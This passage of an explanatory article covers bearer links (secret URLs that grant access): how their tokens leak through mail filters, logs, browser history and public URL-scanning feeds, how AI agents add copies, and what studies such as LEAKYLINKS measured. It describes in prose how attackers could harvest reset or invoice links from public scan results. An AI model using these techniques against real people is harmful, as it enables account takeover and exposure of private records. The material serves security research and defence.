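# AI agents and secret links: how web addresses that grant access leak, and what agents change

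## What bearer links are and who sees them

A bearer link is a web address that gives access to anyone who has it, without checking who they are. Links for sharing a document, resetting a password or opening an emailed invoice are often bearer links. The address contains a token, a random string that the server accepts as proof of permission. Websites use bearer links because the recipient needs no account or password. But much software routinely copies, stores and forwards web addresses, and every copy of a bearer link works as well as the original. AI agents, which are AI models that open pages, read mail and do other work on a person's behalf, now handle these links too.

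Engineers also call bearer links "capability URLs", because whoever has the address has the capability to reach the information behind it. Tennison's *Good Practices for Capability URLs*, a set of recommendations for the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C, the web's main standards body), uses this term. Login protocols also use the word "bearer". *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012) defines a bearer token as one that any holder can use in the same ways as any other holder.

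### Possession and identity

A website can check identity, by having visitors log in and looking up whether their account may see the page, or possession, by looking only at the token. Google Drive offers both for the same file. According to Stanford University's *Share file publicly*, a "Restricted" file opens only for people the owner has chosen, while "Anyone with the link" lets anyone on the internet who has the link open the file without logging in to Google. Stanford's accounts also have a setting in between, which requires visitors to have the link and belong to the university.

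If somebody forwards the address of a restricted file to a stranger, the stranger still has to pass the account check, but with an "anyone with the link" address, the stranger can open the file. Tennison counts this as an advantage in some settings: a person arranging a meeting between several organisations can send one link to a representative of each and trust them to pass it to the right colleagues. But if the link reaches the wrong person, cancelling it usually shuts out the people who were invited too, because everyone has the same address.

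Many bearer links do not look like sharing. Tennison's first example is a password-reset email from Dropbox. Anyone who opens the link before it expires can change that user's password. Pulse Security, in *Sensitive data in URLs* (2026), lists invoices from accounting software and documents that medical applications send to patients. An airline may email a passenger a direct link to a boarding pass. Video-meeting invitations often include the passcode in the address so that a guest can join by clicking.

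Software developers use them as well. A pre-signed file link is a temporary address for a file in cloud storage. AWS's *Download and upload objects with presigned URLs* describes these links as essentially bearer tokens. A link can do no more than the user who created it, and it expires, although a download that starts before the deadline can finish. A webhook address lets one program send messages to another. Slack's *Sending messages using incoming webhooks* says that its webhook addresses contain a secret and tells developers to keep them out of public code repositories. A stranger who finds one can post in a Slack channel, which is a different harm from reading a private file.

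### Unlisted pages

An unlisted page has no access check, so the server sends it to anyone who requests its address, and the owner relies on nobody finding that address. A shop might put next season's prices at `/new-prices` without linking to them, or a company might run a test version of its site under an unannounced hostname.

Tennison's definition covers any "obscure or unguessable" address, which includes both links that contain a token and unlisted pages such as `/new-prices`. An outsider could guess `/new-prices` far more easily than a token with enough entropy (a measure of how hard it is to guess). A site that issues tokens can also cancel them. Flickr lets users expire a guest pass to a private image, and Google Calendar has a button that replaces a calendar's private address with a new one. An unlisted page has no token to cancel, so its owner must move the page, take it down or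 put it behind a login.

The line between bearer links and ordinary links is not perfectly sharp. If a plain file has a long random name, that name effectively serves as a token. *LEAKYLINKS*, Mustafa, Rautenstrauch and colleagues' study of services that check links for fraud and malware, treats any address containing a secret, hard-to-guess value as carrying its own authorisation.

### The parts of an address

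Here is an invented link that a dental clinic's billing software might email to a patient:

`https://northgate-dental.billing.example/invoices/2291?key=b7Qm4xT9vLr2KfZ8#payment`

The opening `https` means the browser and the server encrypt what they send each other. The hostname, `northgate-dental.billing.example`, comes next and names the server. The path, `/invoices/2291`, identifies a page on it. The query follows the question mark and holds extra values for the server, in this case the token. The fragment follows the hash sign, and here it makes the browser scroll to the payment details.

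The token need not sit in the query. Slack puts it in the path, as does the sample invoice link that Pulse Security prints, and some designs put it in the fragment. Where it sits matters, because different parties receive different parts. With an ordinary browser on its default settings, the distribution looks like this:

| Who | Hostname | Path and query | Fragment |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail services, mail filters and chat apps that carry the message | yes | yes | yes |
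| DNS resolver | yes | no | no |
| The website's server and its logs | yes | yes | no |
| Scripts on the page, including other companies' | yes | yes | yes |
| Browser history and extensions | yes | yes | yes |
| The next site, through the Referer header | yes | no | no |

**Mail and chat.** Several services may handle the link before the patient clicks on it. The sender's and recipient's mail services both store the message, and Tennison adds that copies may also sit in mail queues along the way and in unencrypted backups kept by the recipient. Employers often filter incoming mail too. In Mustafa and colleagues' boarding-pass example, the passenger's company automatically submits every link in incoming email to a scanning service, which opens it to look for fraud or malware. Some of these services publish the addresses they have scanned. Pulse Security describes security software on users'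 own computers that submits links in the same way. Chat apps keep the link in the message history, and many also fetch the page to show a preview. Tennison notes that Twitter passed even links in direct messages through its link shortener.

**DNS resolvers.** When the patient clicks, the computer first sends the hostname to a DNS resolver, a server that looks up the matching numerical address. An internet provider, an employer or a public service such as Google runs the resolver, which receives the full hostname but not the rest of the link. Wicinski (2021) wrote in *DNS Privacy Considerations* that almost all of these lookups were still unencrypted, even when the page itself was encrypted, though encrypted lookups were spreading. An eavesdropper could thus learn that somebody in the house is dealing with Northgate Dental, but could not open the invoice.

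Some organisations collect the answers to such lookups in searchable databases, a practice called passive DNS. According to a 2024 definition from the IETF, the internet's technical standards body, users can search these databases to find when a hostname first appeared or which hostnames point to a particular numerical address. With DNS alone, a person must already know a name to look it up. Passive DNS removes that obstacle, and Wicinski lists it among the ways supposedly private names leak. This is a serious risk for a page whose only protection is an unannounced hostname, but it does little harm to a bearer link with its token in the path or query, because the database never receives that part.

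**Servers and logs.** The clinic's server needs the path and query to find the invoice, and servers commonly log each request. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, 2022), the standard for how browsers and servers exchange pages, warns that addresses are "intended to be shared, not secured", and that many servers, browsers and machines in between record or display them where others might look. For the same reason, Jones and Hardt advise developers to send a token in a request header, a labelled line that travels with the request but outside the address, and to put it in the query only when no other way is possible. An emailed link has to carry the token in the address, because clicking it sends a plain request to which the sender cannot attach a header.

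**Fragments.** The browser does not send the fragment when it requests a page. A designer can therefore put the token there and have a script on the page read it, which keeps the token out of the ordinary request log. This protection is partial because extensions and scripts can read the fragment, including scripts that the site has embedded from advertising or analytics companies. Fielding also warns that if the first site redirects the browser to a second one, the browser may carry the fragment along, and scripts on the second site can then read it.

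The browser keeps the full address in its history, and any service that synchronises that history between devices holds a copy. The address also appears in the address bar, where an audience can read it during a presentation. Tennison mentions that a stray space in a pasted address makes the browser treat it as a search, which sends the link to the search engine. Tennison drafted this list in 2014, and particular products may have changed since.

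### The Referer header

When a user follows a link from one page to another, the browser can send the new site the address of the page the user came from, in a request header named Referer (a misspelling of "referrer"). web.dev's *Referer and Referrer-Policy best practices* explains that the browser can also send this header when a page loads an image, frame or script from another server, even if the user clicks nothing.

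By default, browsers used to send the path and query of the current page's address with requests to any other site, provided that the new connection was no less secure than the old one. If the patient had clicked through from the invoice to a payment company, that company would have received the key. Such leaks were a standard objection to bearer links when the W3C took up the subject. In 2014, W3C's *Capability URLs* invited comments on Tennison's draft after private addresses for shared documents had leaked to third parties. A reviewer objected in *Comments on "Good Practices for Capability URLs" FPWD* that the web does not generally keep addresses secret and that the W3C should not encourage bearer links.

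The current default, `strict-origin-when-cross-origin`, is much stricter. MDN's *Referrer-Policy header* describes three cases. A request within the same origin (the same protocol, hostname and port) still carries the path and query. A request to another site carries only the origin, so the payment company would receive `https://northgate-dental.billing.example/` and no key. A request from an encrypted page to an unencrypted one carries no referring address. Van Cleve (2020), in *Intent to Ship*, announced the change for Chrome. The Can I use browser-support table *headers HTTP header* lists the new default in every version of Chrome and Edge from 85, Firefox from 87 and Safari from 15, up to those of 2026. Safari's behaviour differs in some details.

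A website can still override the browser's safe default. The setting `unsafe-url` makes the browser send the path and query with every request, and a developer can also loosen the policy for a single link or image. Since version 93, Firefox has ignored the looser settings for requests to other sites, but only in private browsing or with strict tracking protection on. No Referer policy stops another company's script on the page from reading the address. For a patient with a recent browser, Referer is therefore a minor way for the link to leak unless the clinic's developers have made a mistake, and embedded scripts are a bigger concern.

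### When the secret disappears along the way

Many sites let people log in by email instead of with a password. The user enters an email address, and the site sends a link with a token in it. When the user clicks the link, the server checks the token, gives the browser a cookie (a small piece of data that the browser sends back with each later request to that site) and redirects the browser to another page, such as `/dashboard`. The server then uses the cookie to identify the user's account.

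Mustafa and colleagues point out that the final address may hold no secret. A user who copies `/dashboard` from the address bar and sends it to a friend gives the friend no access, because the friend's browser lacks the cookie. The link in the email is more dangerous, because anyone who opens it while the token still works is logged in as the account's owner. A check that looks only at the final address will miss this risk.

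Some sites write the token into each further link on the site instead of redirecting to a clean address, so the address of every page the user visits can give access to anyone who obtains it.

### Agents and their context

An agent is an AI model that takes actions with tools, such as opening web pages, searching a mailbox or running code, whereas a plain chatbot only writes replies. An agent works in a loop. Suppose the dental patient asks an agent to find this month's unpaid bills. A program sends the model the request and a description of the available tools. The model writes an instruction to search the mailbox, and the program runs the search and adds the messages it finds to the model's input. The model might then write an instruction to open the clinic's link, and the program adds the invoice page to the input as well. The loop ends when the model writes its answer.

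The model's context is the text available to it at any moment, including the user's request, the messages and pages the agent has opened, and the results from its tools. If the clinic's email enters the context with its links intact, the full bearer link, including its token and fragment, becomes ordinary text that the model can repeat in an answer, a file or a later instruction.

Nothing in the form of an address marks it as secret. Tennison noted that browsers cannot tell a capability URL from a normal one, and suggested that the W3C look into a marker. A language model is somewhat better able to tell them apart because it can read the surrounding email. It may infer that a link containing `key=` under the words "your invoice" is private. It has less context when somebody pastes only a document link into a chat.

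## What a secret address can guarantee in theory

A stranger can get a working bearer link by guessing its token or by finding a copy of the link. A website can make guessing impractical by choosing a long random token, but it has much less control over copies because other people's software makes most of them.

### Guessing

Suppose a site picks each token at random, with *b* bits of entropy, so there are 2^b possible tokens. If *N* links are live, each guess has an *N* / 2^b chance of opening one of them. An attacker therefore needs about 2^b / *N* guesses, on average, to open one.

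*N* matters only because this attacker will accept any live link. Someone who wants one particular patient's invoice gains nothing from the other live links and must find one address among 2^b possibilities.

A service whose links end in six characters, each a digit or an upper- or lower-case letter, has 62^6, or about 5.7 × 10^10, possible addresses, which is just under 36 bits. If 100 million links are live, about one guess in 570 succeeds. At ten guesses a second, an attacker opens a stranger's link about once a minute. Researchers have found services open to this kind of enumeration (the section on text-message links gives their measurements). A 128-bit token is infeasible to guess, even with a billion live links and a million guesses a second.

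| Token | Live links | Average tries per hit | Time at 1,000 tries a second | Time at 1 million tries a second |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 6 characters from 62 | 100 million | 570 | 0.6 seconds | under a millisecond |
| 64 bits | 1 million | 1.8 × 10^13 | 585 years | 7 months |
| 64 bits | 1 billion | 1.8 × 10^10 | 7 months | 5 hours |
| 128 bits | 1 billion | 3.4 × 10^29 | 10^19 years | 10^16 years |

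The first 64-bit row uses the assumptions in Close's *Web-key*, which proposes building web applications around bearer links. Close considered 64 bits enough for many applications and estimated that an attacker would need 292 years for an even chance of one hit. The next row shows how much that time depends on the size and speed of the site. The attacker must send every guess to the site, since only the site can check whether a token is valid, so the site's capacity limits the rate of guessing.

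Close's 292 years is half the table's 585. MITRE, which runs a public catalogue of software weaknesses, also halves the figure in its formula for guessing session identifiers. Halving is right for a single live link, because an attacker who never repeats a guess finds it, on average, halfway through the search. With many live links, the average is close to 2^b / *N*. A factor of two equals one bit, so it doesn't change any of the conclusions here.

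Tennison recommends at least 120 bits and accepts a version 4 UUID, a standard format for random identifiers. The token in the dental clinic's link has 16 characters from the same set of 62, or about 95 bits, but only if the billing software chose them at random. A long token can have very little entropy. In MITRE's example, a site hands out identifiers in ascending order, so anyone who has one can work out the next, however many digits it has. Tennison also warns against passing a bearer link through a link shortener whose links are easier to enumerate. If the clinic shortened its link to six characters to fit a text message, an attacker could ignore the 95-bit token and guess the short code.

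### Leaking

Entropy does not protect a secret address once somebody has a copy of it. A mail filter that forwards links to a scanning service will forward a link with a 128-bit token just as it would one with a six-character token, and the recipient can open either in a browser.

A simple model shows how the risk grows with copying. Let *n* be the number of copies of a link, and *p* the chance that a given copy reaches an outsider while the link still works. If the copies are independent, the chance that none of them leaks is (1 − *p*)^n, so the chance that at least one leaks is

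1 − (1 − *p*)^n

Suppose the clinic's invoice link is stored in eight places, including two mailboxes, a mail filter, a server log and a synchronised browser history, and each has a 1% chance of leaking. The link then leaks with probability 1 − 0.99^8, or 7.7%. If the patient asks an agent to find unpaid bills, the link also ends up in the agent's saved conversation, a tool log, a summary file and a message to the patient's partner. With twelve copies, the probability of a leak rises to 11.4%. For a clinic that sends 10,000 such links, the expected number of leaked invoices rises from about 770 to 1,140. The 1% is invented, and the real chance surely varies from place to place.

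This variation in risk matters more than the number of copies. If eleven copies each have a 0.1% chance of leaking and a twelfth has a 20% chance, the chance that at least one leaks is about 21%. Deleting the risky copy lowers that to about 1%, while deleting the other eleven lowers it only to 20%. An agent that adds four well-protected copies may therefore do less harm than one that posts the link once in a busy channel.

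Real copies are not independent either. An intruder who takes over the patient's mail account gets the clinic's message, the agent's emailed summary and anything the patient forwarded. Shared causes like this make the chance of at least one leak lower than the formula gives. If all twelve copies leak together or not at all, the chance is 1%. But a shared cause, such as a wrong setting in a mail filter that serves thousands of patients, can also expose all their invoices on the same day, even if the average loss over the years is no higher.

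Once a link leaks onto a public page, search engines and archives may store copies of it, so the owner has more places to remove it from. The model leaves this out because it treats *n* as fixed.

### The argument for bearer links

Some people defend putting permissions in addresses, even though addresses spread easily. They draw on decades of operating-system research into capabilities, which are references that both identify a thing and give permission to use it.

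Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells the story that made the case for many of them. At Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, a compiler (a program that translates code) had permission to write to its own directory so that it could record usage statistics. The directory also held the company's billing file. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user entered the name of the billing file. The user didn't have permission to overwrite that file, but the compiler did, and it replaced the billing data with the debugging output.

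Hardy concluded that the compiler held authority from both its owner and its user, and had no way to specify which authority to use for each write. In a capability system, the user would have given the compiler a capability for the output file instead of typing a file name. A user without a capability for the billing file could not have made the compiler write to it.

Close argues that ordinary web logins recreate this problem. Suppose a logged-in user of a webmail site visits a hostile page. A script on the page submits a hidden form to the mail site's forwarding settings, with the attacker's email address filled in. The browser attaches the user's cookie, as it does for any request to the mail site, and the site starts forwarding the user's mail. Sites can defend themselves by putting a random secret in each genuine form. If the permission to change forwarding were a bearer link, the attacker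 could not write the form, because they would have no way to know the address.

The same design allows narrow permissions. Close imagines an outside service that needs to read one mail folder. A password would give the service the whole account, including the power to send mail, whereas a link can let it read only that folder. Links also let people delegate without accounts. For example, a user could send a friend a link to the friend's own entry in an address book, and the friend could keep the entry up to date. Close adds that a phisher can trick a person into typing a password into a fake login page, but a browser sends a link's key only to the site named in the link, after checking that site's certificate.

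AI agents have revived the argument. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) predicts that agents will multiply confused deputies and proposes capabilities as the answer. An agent reading a mailbox resembles Hardy's compiler because it works with its user's authority while reading text that strangers wrote. If the agent has no other access, giving it a link to one invoice instead of the whole mailbox greatly reduces the damage a stranger's text can do.

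### Where the analogy breaks down

The strongest guarantees in capability research do not carry over to links, because they depend on keeping capabilities separate from ordinary data. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) argues against three common beliefs: that capability systems are formally equivalent to access control lists (lists, kept with each file, of who may use it), that capability systems cannot stop permissions from spreading, and that nobody can take a permission back. In the object-capability systems that the paper defends, the operating system or programming language enforces the separation from data. Alice can pass Bob a capability only if she already has one that lets her send messages to Bob. An administrator can therefore keep permissions away from Bob by making sure that no chain of connections reaches him.

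They contrast this with a model in which capabilities are like keys that people can copy and give to anyone. In that model, they write, the system cannot stop permissions from spreading, and nobody can take one back. A bearer link is much closer to a copyable key, because anyone who can send text can send the link, and no part of the web checks whether the sender was entitled to reach the recipient.

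Noah Mendelsohn made the same point to the W3C in *Comments on "Good Practices for Capability URLs" FPWD*. Systems with strong guarantees control who creates, copies and transmits capabilities. Unix does this for open files, but the web doesn't for addresses. Mendelsohn repeated the objection in a 2023 message (quoted in a reply, Appelquist 2023), after Google's search engine had indexed shared conversations with the company's Bard chatbot.

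Making access revocable is easier. Miller and colleagues describe a setup in which Alice gives Bob a reference to a forwarder, which passes his requests on to the resource and which she can switch off. If she does, Bob loses access, and so does Ted if Bob has shared the reference with him. A website can get a similar effect without shutting everyone out at once by issuing each recipient a separate link and disabling only the one that leaked, as Tennison suggests.

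Some security engineers doubt the wider capability programme as well. In a mailing-list thread named after the *Myths* paper, Gutmann (2015) objected that one can "demolish" almost any myth with well-chosen examples and solutions that need not work in practice. In the same thread, Frantz (2015) quotes Jerry Leichter's complaint that the paper meets objections by adding extensions to the model. These criticisms are brief, and one of the main claims in *Myths* has since gained support. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk proved that access-control systems and object capabilities are fundamentally different. But the critics have a point about bearer links, because the web would need rebuilding before it could offer the guarantees in *Myths*.

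Links also provide a poor record of who used them. A server can log the account name when an employee opens a restricted file, but for a bearer link it can log only that a request arrived with the right token. The 2014 draft of Tennison's recommendations, published by the W3C, observed that legitimate and illegitimate visits look the same apart from clues such as the visitor's IP address and browser type. Giving each recipient a separate link would show whose link leaked, but not who used it.

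In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro judge access control by how well it spreads the permissions people need to cooperate while limiting the spread of those that create vulnerabilities. Bearer links make permissions very easy to share but offer almost no way to limit their spread.

Close had answers to several of these worries. Encryption hides the address from machines along the route, operators can strip keys from server logs, and users can encrypt their stored bookmarks. These answers work best when the site and its user control the places where copies end up. Even then, Close saw an exception in browsers that reported every visited address to a central phishing-detection service, which users had to trust to keep the addresses confidential.

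### What the standards bodies decided

The W3C's Technical Architecture Group, which advises on the design of the web, argued about bearer links for years. Mendelsohn (2010), then its chair, told Close that the group had taken no position on the arguments in *Web-key*, though members had found them thought-provoking. The 2014 draft called the risk of exposure "very high" and advised developers not to use capability URLs by default, because they were secure only in tightly controlled circumstances.

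The group then published Tennison's final text as a finding, a document that advises developers without binding them. The finding is milder. Tennison writes that the risk "can be quite high" unless developers add safeguards, and that they should weigh the costs and benefits of capability URLs against those of other methods. She considers the recommended safeguards adequate in many cases, but says capability URLs will not be secure enough for some applications. One of her harder cases is a password reset for a high-value system, because even if the link expires after 15 minutes, a motivated attacker might intercept and use it in that time.

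In *Capability URLs Best Practice*, a forum post asking for comments on the group's draft, torgo (2014) wrote that the document was "not intended to discourage the use of this pattern". A commenter replied that the draft mixed up lasting secret links with one-shot links such as password resets. In the copies model, every copy of a lasting link stays dangerous, but copies of a one-shot link are harmless once it has been used and the site has cancelled it.

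The OAuth standards are stricter. OAuth lets one application use a person's account on another service with an access token, without learning the password. In 2012, Jones and Hardt advised that applications "SHOULD NOT" put such tokens in page addresses, a term that in internet standards allows exceptions for good reason. They described how to put a token in the query part of an address only to document existing use. A participant in the mailing-list discussion *Reserved URI query parameter in draft-ietf-oauth-v2-bearer* defended the practice because systems can pass around such an address as a unit, with its authorisation included. In 2025, *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security*, by Lodderstedt, Bradley and colleagues, removed the exceptions. Applications "MUST NOT" put access tokens in the query, because they can end up in browser history.

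This rule does not cover share links or emailed invoices, which have to carry their tokens in the address. But the rule exists because browsers keep addresses, and they keep the patient's link too.

OAuth still puts one kind of secret in addresses. After the user approves a request, the service sends the browser back to the application with a short code in the address, and the application exchanges that code for a token. Lodderstedt and colleagues accept this because the code works only once and the service can tie it to a second secret, which the application created at the start and never puts in the address. Somebody who finds the code in a browser's history cannot use it without that second secret. They also recommend tying each access token to a particular sender, who must prove they know another secret, so that it is no longer a bearer token.

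### Is it security by obscurity?

Critics often dismiss secret addresses as "security by obscurity", protection that lasts only while attackers don't know how a system works. One way to test this criticism is to publish everything about the design except the secret itself.

A 128-bit token passes this test because an attacker who knows the site's source code, the format of its links and the exact length of its tokens would still need the 10^16 years in the table to guess one. In that respect the token is like a password, but far stronger than most passwords people choose. Close made this argument against the W3C's description of web architecture, which had compared using secret addresses to hiding some of a building's entrances. Close replied that an intruder can walk around a building and find every door, but cannot search through all the possible keys.

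"Obscurity" is a fair label for most unlisted pages, because an address such as `/new-prices` is easy to guess. An attacker who knows only that shops give such pages ordinary names can try 100,000 likely ones in under three hours, at ten tries a second. A list of that size corresponds to fewer than 17 bits of randomness. A long random name would help in the path, where it would work as a token, but not in the hostname, which passive DNS may reveal.

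Critics of the 128-bit link can still reasonably complain that it leaks more easily than a password. Browsers hide a password as the user types it, and well-built sites store it only in scrambled form. But browsers display a bearer link in full and save it to the history, and even those sites may write it to a log.

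## Links found in public scanning feeds and archives

A stranger who cannot guess the dental clinic's token may still find the link on a public website. Some scanning services publish the addresses they check, web archives keep others, and anyone can search both. Researchers have searched these records for links that open private pages, and some have planted their own links to see who would open them.

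### How a mail filter makes a link public

Suppose the dental patient gave the clinic a work email address, and the employer's mail filter submits the invoice link to a scanning service. The service opens the link in its own browser, checks whether the page is a phishing site (a fake page that steals passwords) and stores a report. If the filter requests a public scan, or doesn't specify and the default is public, the service publishes the report on its website, perhaps before the patient has read the email.

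At urlscan.io, one of the largest of these services, the report includes the address, a screenshot and the page's full HTML, according to Positive Security's *urlscan.io's SOAR spot* (2022). Visitors can search old reports without an account. If the clinic cancels the link, nobody new can open the invoice, but the screenshot stays up until urlscan.io removes it.

urlscan.io's *Scan Visibility Best Practices* (2022) describes three levels of visibility. Anyone can find a public scan. Customers of the company's paid product, whom it describes as vetted researchers and reputable corporations, can also see unlisted scans. Only the submitter and their team can see a private one.

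Employers often connect their mail to urlscan.io through "security orchestration" software, which runs automatic routines on incoming messages. A scan's visibility then depends on the command in the routine, the connector's settings and the employer's urlscan.io account settings, so there are several places to make a mistake. Even an employer that chose the right settings could publish links because of a bug that Positive Security describes in a connector for Palo Alto Networks' software. One option defaulted to public and overrode the other settings until a fix in May 2022. At Cloudflare, a large internet infrastructure company, scans submitted through the programming interface are public by default. A developer who copies the simplest sample request from Cloudflare's *URL Scanner* documentation gets a public scan.

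In Theobald (2026), *When Security Becomes a Risk Factor*, Ali Mustafa, the lead researcher on LEAKYLINKS, suggests that scanning services publish feeds to advertise how fast and thorough they are, and to let security teams share what they learn about suspicious sites. urlscan.io encourages public or unlisted scans to support this sharing. Even so, most of its scans are not public. On the day Positive Security checked in 2022, about 20% were. The pseudonymous researcher Vin01 later reported a share of 24%, or roughly 400,000 scans in a day, in *Exploring Private URL Leaks And Ongoing Abuse of Government Web Services*.

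People also submit links by hand, sometimes because a security product has alarmed them, and one false alarm can make many links leak at once. For two days in April 2025, Microsoft's email service marked genuine Adobe messages as spam. TechRadar's *Microsoft fixes annoying bug which marked Adobe emails as spam* quotes the scanning service ANY.RUN, which saw its users upload more than a thousand Adobe files with sensitive data from hundreds of companies. ANY.RUN then made those analyses private.

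### Case reports from 2022 to 2024

GitHub, where developers store code, also hosts web pages for its customers. To catch phishing, it sent each new page to urlscan.io. According to *How to Categorize and Prevent Risks of Sensitive Links in URLScan* (Rijal, Nipper and Emek, 2022), GitHub submitted these pages as public scans between January and September 2021, which revealed the names of private code repositories. GitHub told the affected customers in February 2022.

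GitHub's notice prompted Positive Security to search urlscan.io for other private links. The team found password-reset pages, contracts awaiting a signature, PayPal invoices, shared Google Drive documents and Zoom invitations to court hearings. To test whether mail filters were the source, the team emailed 23 people whose addresses had leaked through such scans and put a unique link at the end of each message. Nine of the 23 links appeared in urlscan.io's public results. The next day the team emailed another 24 people, and 12 of the new links appeared.

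These recipients were not typical, because the team had picked people whose links had already leaked. But the result shows why even a trivial leak can matter. A leaked unsubscribe page may reveal only an email address, but the leak suggests that the owner's mail filter publishes links from incoming messages. An attacker could confirm this with a test message, request a password reset for that person at a bank or social network, and read the reset link in the public results. Positive Security described this attack but did not report a real case of it.

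Rijal and colleagues, who worked on security at Tinder, searched for the invitations that employers send new staff to join one single sign-on service, which lets an employee into many company applications with one login. They found 1,300 invitation links, and 20 to 50 new, working ones appeared each day. A stranger who opened such a link before the new employee did could set the password and second login factor, then use the company's internal applications as that employee.

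Symantec's *Defending Data Requires More than Good Intentions*, an undated study of 700 business-software domains in urlscan.io's index, reports about 600 links that exposed sensitive information, on 76 of the domains. Following some of the links also triggered an action, such as accepting an appointment or removing someone from a mailing list, so an automatic scan could do harm even if no stranger saw the results.

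In March 2024, Vin01 reported leaks similar to urlscan.io's at Hybrid Analysis and Cloudflare's scanner. The leaked material included tax documents, photos of credit cards and recordings from smart-home devices. Vin01 also used decoy links to test urlscan.io's unlisted scans, which are visible to fewer people than public ones. Unknown people or programs opened the links several times within an hour.

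urlscan.io had reacted to the early reports in 2022. It added rules that delete scans matching known patterns, contacted customers who submitted many public scans, and let employers set a maximum visibility for their whole team. Leaks continued. In January 2026, Pulse Security found a PDF with patient details and a photo album of medical documents through urlscan.io. It also obtained a list of 24,179 shortened OneDrive links from AlienVault OTX, a database where security teams share signs of attacks. Some of them opened documents, though Pulse Security did not count how many, and it was not sure how the links had got there.

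Most of these researchers searched for patterns they already knew, such as the format of one company's reset links. Such searches can prove that leaks exist, but they miss any link whose format the researcher did not think of, and they give little idea of how common leaks are.

### LEAKYLINKS: three weeks of six public feeds

Mustafa and colleagues designed LEAKYLINKS to work without a list of known patterns. They first surveyed 20 scanning services, using only free or trial plans. Nine had no public feed. Four published only the site's base address, which cannot contain a token. PhishTank's feed consisted mainly of malicious addresses. The other six published full addresses from ordinary security work. From October 10 to November 1, 2025, the team collected all 2,286,501 unique links in those six feeds.

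The pipeline had four stages:

1. **Filter.** It discarded base addresses with no path or query, which made up 84% of the collection, and links that Google's Safe Browsing service had flagged as malicious. A browser then tried to open the remaining 332,647 links soon after they appeared, and 305,539 of them loaded.
2. **Token check.** It looked in the final address for a string of at least eight characters that might be a token. About 74% of the loaded pages passed and went straight to the last stage.
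3. **Page-difference check.** Some of the other pages could have come from emailed login links, where a redirect removes the token from the address. For pages that had redirected, the pipeline cleared the browser's cookies and other stored data and loaded the final address again. If a dashboard turned into a login form, the original link had probably logged the browser in. This check kept 2,918 pages.
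4. **Vision model.** An AI model that can read images examined a screenshot of each of the 229,256 remaining pages. The prompt told it to ignore public contact details and to call a page sensitive only if it could quote something private on the screen. The model ran on the researchers' own servers, so no private page went to an outside company.

The token check required only 2 bits of Shannon entropy per character, which here measures how varied a string's characters are, not how hard it is to guess. The word "dashboard" scores about 2.7 and would pass. The team deliberately set the threshold low to avoid discarding real leaks, so the pipeline relied mostly on the vision model to separate private pages from public ones.

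The model flagged 4,417 pages, on 1,843 domains, as containing sensitive personal information. That is about 190 a day. The last column of this table divides each service's flagged pages by the links left after filtering:

| Service | Links collected | Left after filtering | Sensitive pages | Share of filtered links |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| urlscan.io | 1,454,914 | 164,315 | 1,861 | 1.1% |
| URLQuery | 336,940 | 124,386 | 897 | 0.7% |
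| ANY.RUN | 36,811 | 23,169 | 778 | 3.4% |
| Hybrid Analysis | 25,522 | 16,061 | 550 | 3.4% |
| Cloudflare Radar | 443,576 | 7,382 | 224 | 3.0% |
| Joe Sandbox | 5,049 | 3,497 | 107 | 3.1% |

urlscan.io had the most sensitive pages because it had the most links. On four of the other services, a full link was nearly three times as likely to open a sensitive page. Cloudflare's feed was large but consisted almost entirely of base addresses. Only 1.7% of its links had a path or query, down from about 20% in a pilot study that ended in April 2025. The researchers had told Cloudflare about the leaks after the pilot, and they believe the drop is connected.

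Only 30 of the 4,417 pages passed the page-difference check, so working login links of that kind were rare in the feeds. One possible reason is that the scanning service opens each link before publishing it, which would use up a link that works only once. Pulse Security saw something similar with password-sharing sites, where most of the links no longer showed anything because someone or something had already viewed them.

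### How accurate the count is

Mustafa and colleagues checked 300 of the flagged pages by hand and found that 291 really were sensitive, a precision of 97%. They also checked 2,250 pages that the model had passed as harmless and found 12 sensitive ones. Applying both error rates to the whole set gives their estimate of the true total:

4,417 − 133 false alarms + 1,191 missed pages ≈ 5,475

The number of missed pages is the less certain part because it rests on 12 cases. The paper's 95% confidence interval for that error rate puts the total between about 5,000 and 6,400.

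The 300 flagged pages came from 300 different domains, so a provider with hundreds of flagged pages counted for no more than a site with one. If the model was systematically wrong about a big provider, this check could easily have missed it. But the estimate also leaves out 76,283 pages that the earlier checks discarded, and anything behind a button or a cookie banner, because the researchers didn't let their browser click on strangers' pages. On balance, the true number of exposed pages in these feeds is probably higher than 4,417.

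### What the pages contained

The largest group, 1,411 pages or 32%, dealt with mailing-list preferences and unsubscribing. Many of these pages do little harm unless an attacker uses them to find a leaky mail filter, as Positive Security described. Login and verification pages, including password-reset forms, made up 17%, documents and records 12%, and account pages 11%. Bills, payments and orders made up 9%, and the dental invoice would belong in this group.

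In the worst cases, the researchers found visa applications, government documents and files marked as military-classified. One electronic visa page showed the holder's name, address, date of birth and passport details, with working controls for editing them. Many of the login and reset pages might have let a stranger take over an account. The researchers did not try this, for ethical reasons, so the number that would have worked is unknown.

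Of the 1,843 domains, 210 were among the 10,000 most popular on the web. An email security provider had the most pages, with 273. These listed the spam it had caught, which revealed its customers' email addresses. A major office suite was second with 162, including private photos and contracts.

Many of the links contained words such as "mail" or "click", or pointed to a domain that Microsoft Outlook uses to check links. This suggests that mail filters submitted a lot of them, but only the scanning services could confirm this. The published counts therefore do not show how many links came from filters, people or AI agents.

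In the earlier reports, a researcher had to know what a company's private links looked like before searching for them. A vision model removes that requirement because it examines the page itself. The project's computation took 50 hours on eight graphics processors, and the code is public, so an attacker with a modest budget could probably sort these feeds in the same way.

### Who opens published links

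Mustafa and colleagues also set up decoy pages, submitted their links to the six services as public scans and recorded the visitors. Each address contained a number and a code for the service, so a visitor was very unlikely to find it except through the feed.

The researchers compared four types of link. The first used the plain path `/news/`, and the second used a more tempting one, `/secret/login/`. The third added a long random identifier to that login path, and the fourth put values named `authCode` and `key` in the query. All four led to nearly the same page, which offered a form, a QR code, database files, a fake credit card number and fake credentials for Amazon's cloud. Some of these items would alert the researchers if anyone opened or used them.

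The team ignored the first visit to each link, which was presumably the scanning service itself. That left 2,710 visits from at most 901 different IP addresses. The paper's total of 1,081 counts an address again for each service whose links it visited, and 180 addresses visited links from at least two services. Links that looked sensitive did not attract more interest:

| Type of link | Visits | Visits from suspicious addresses |
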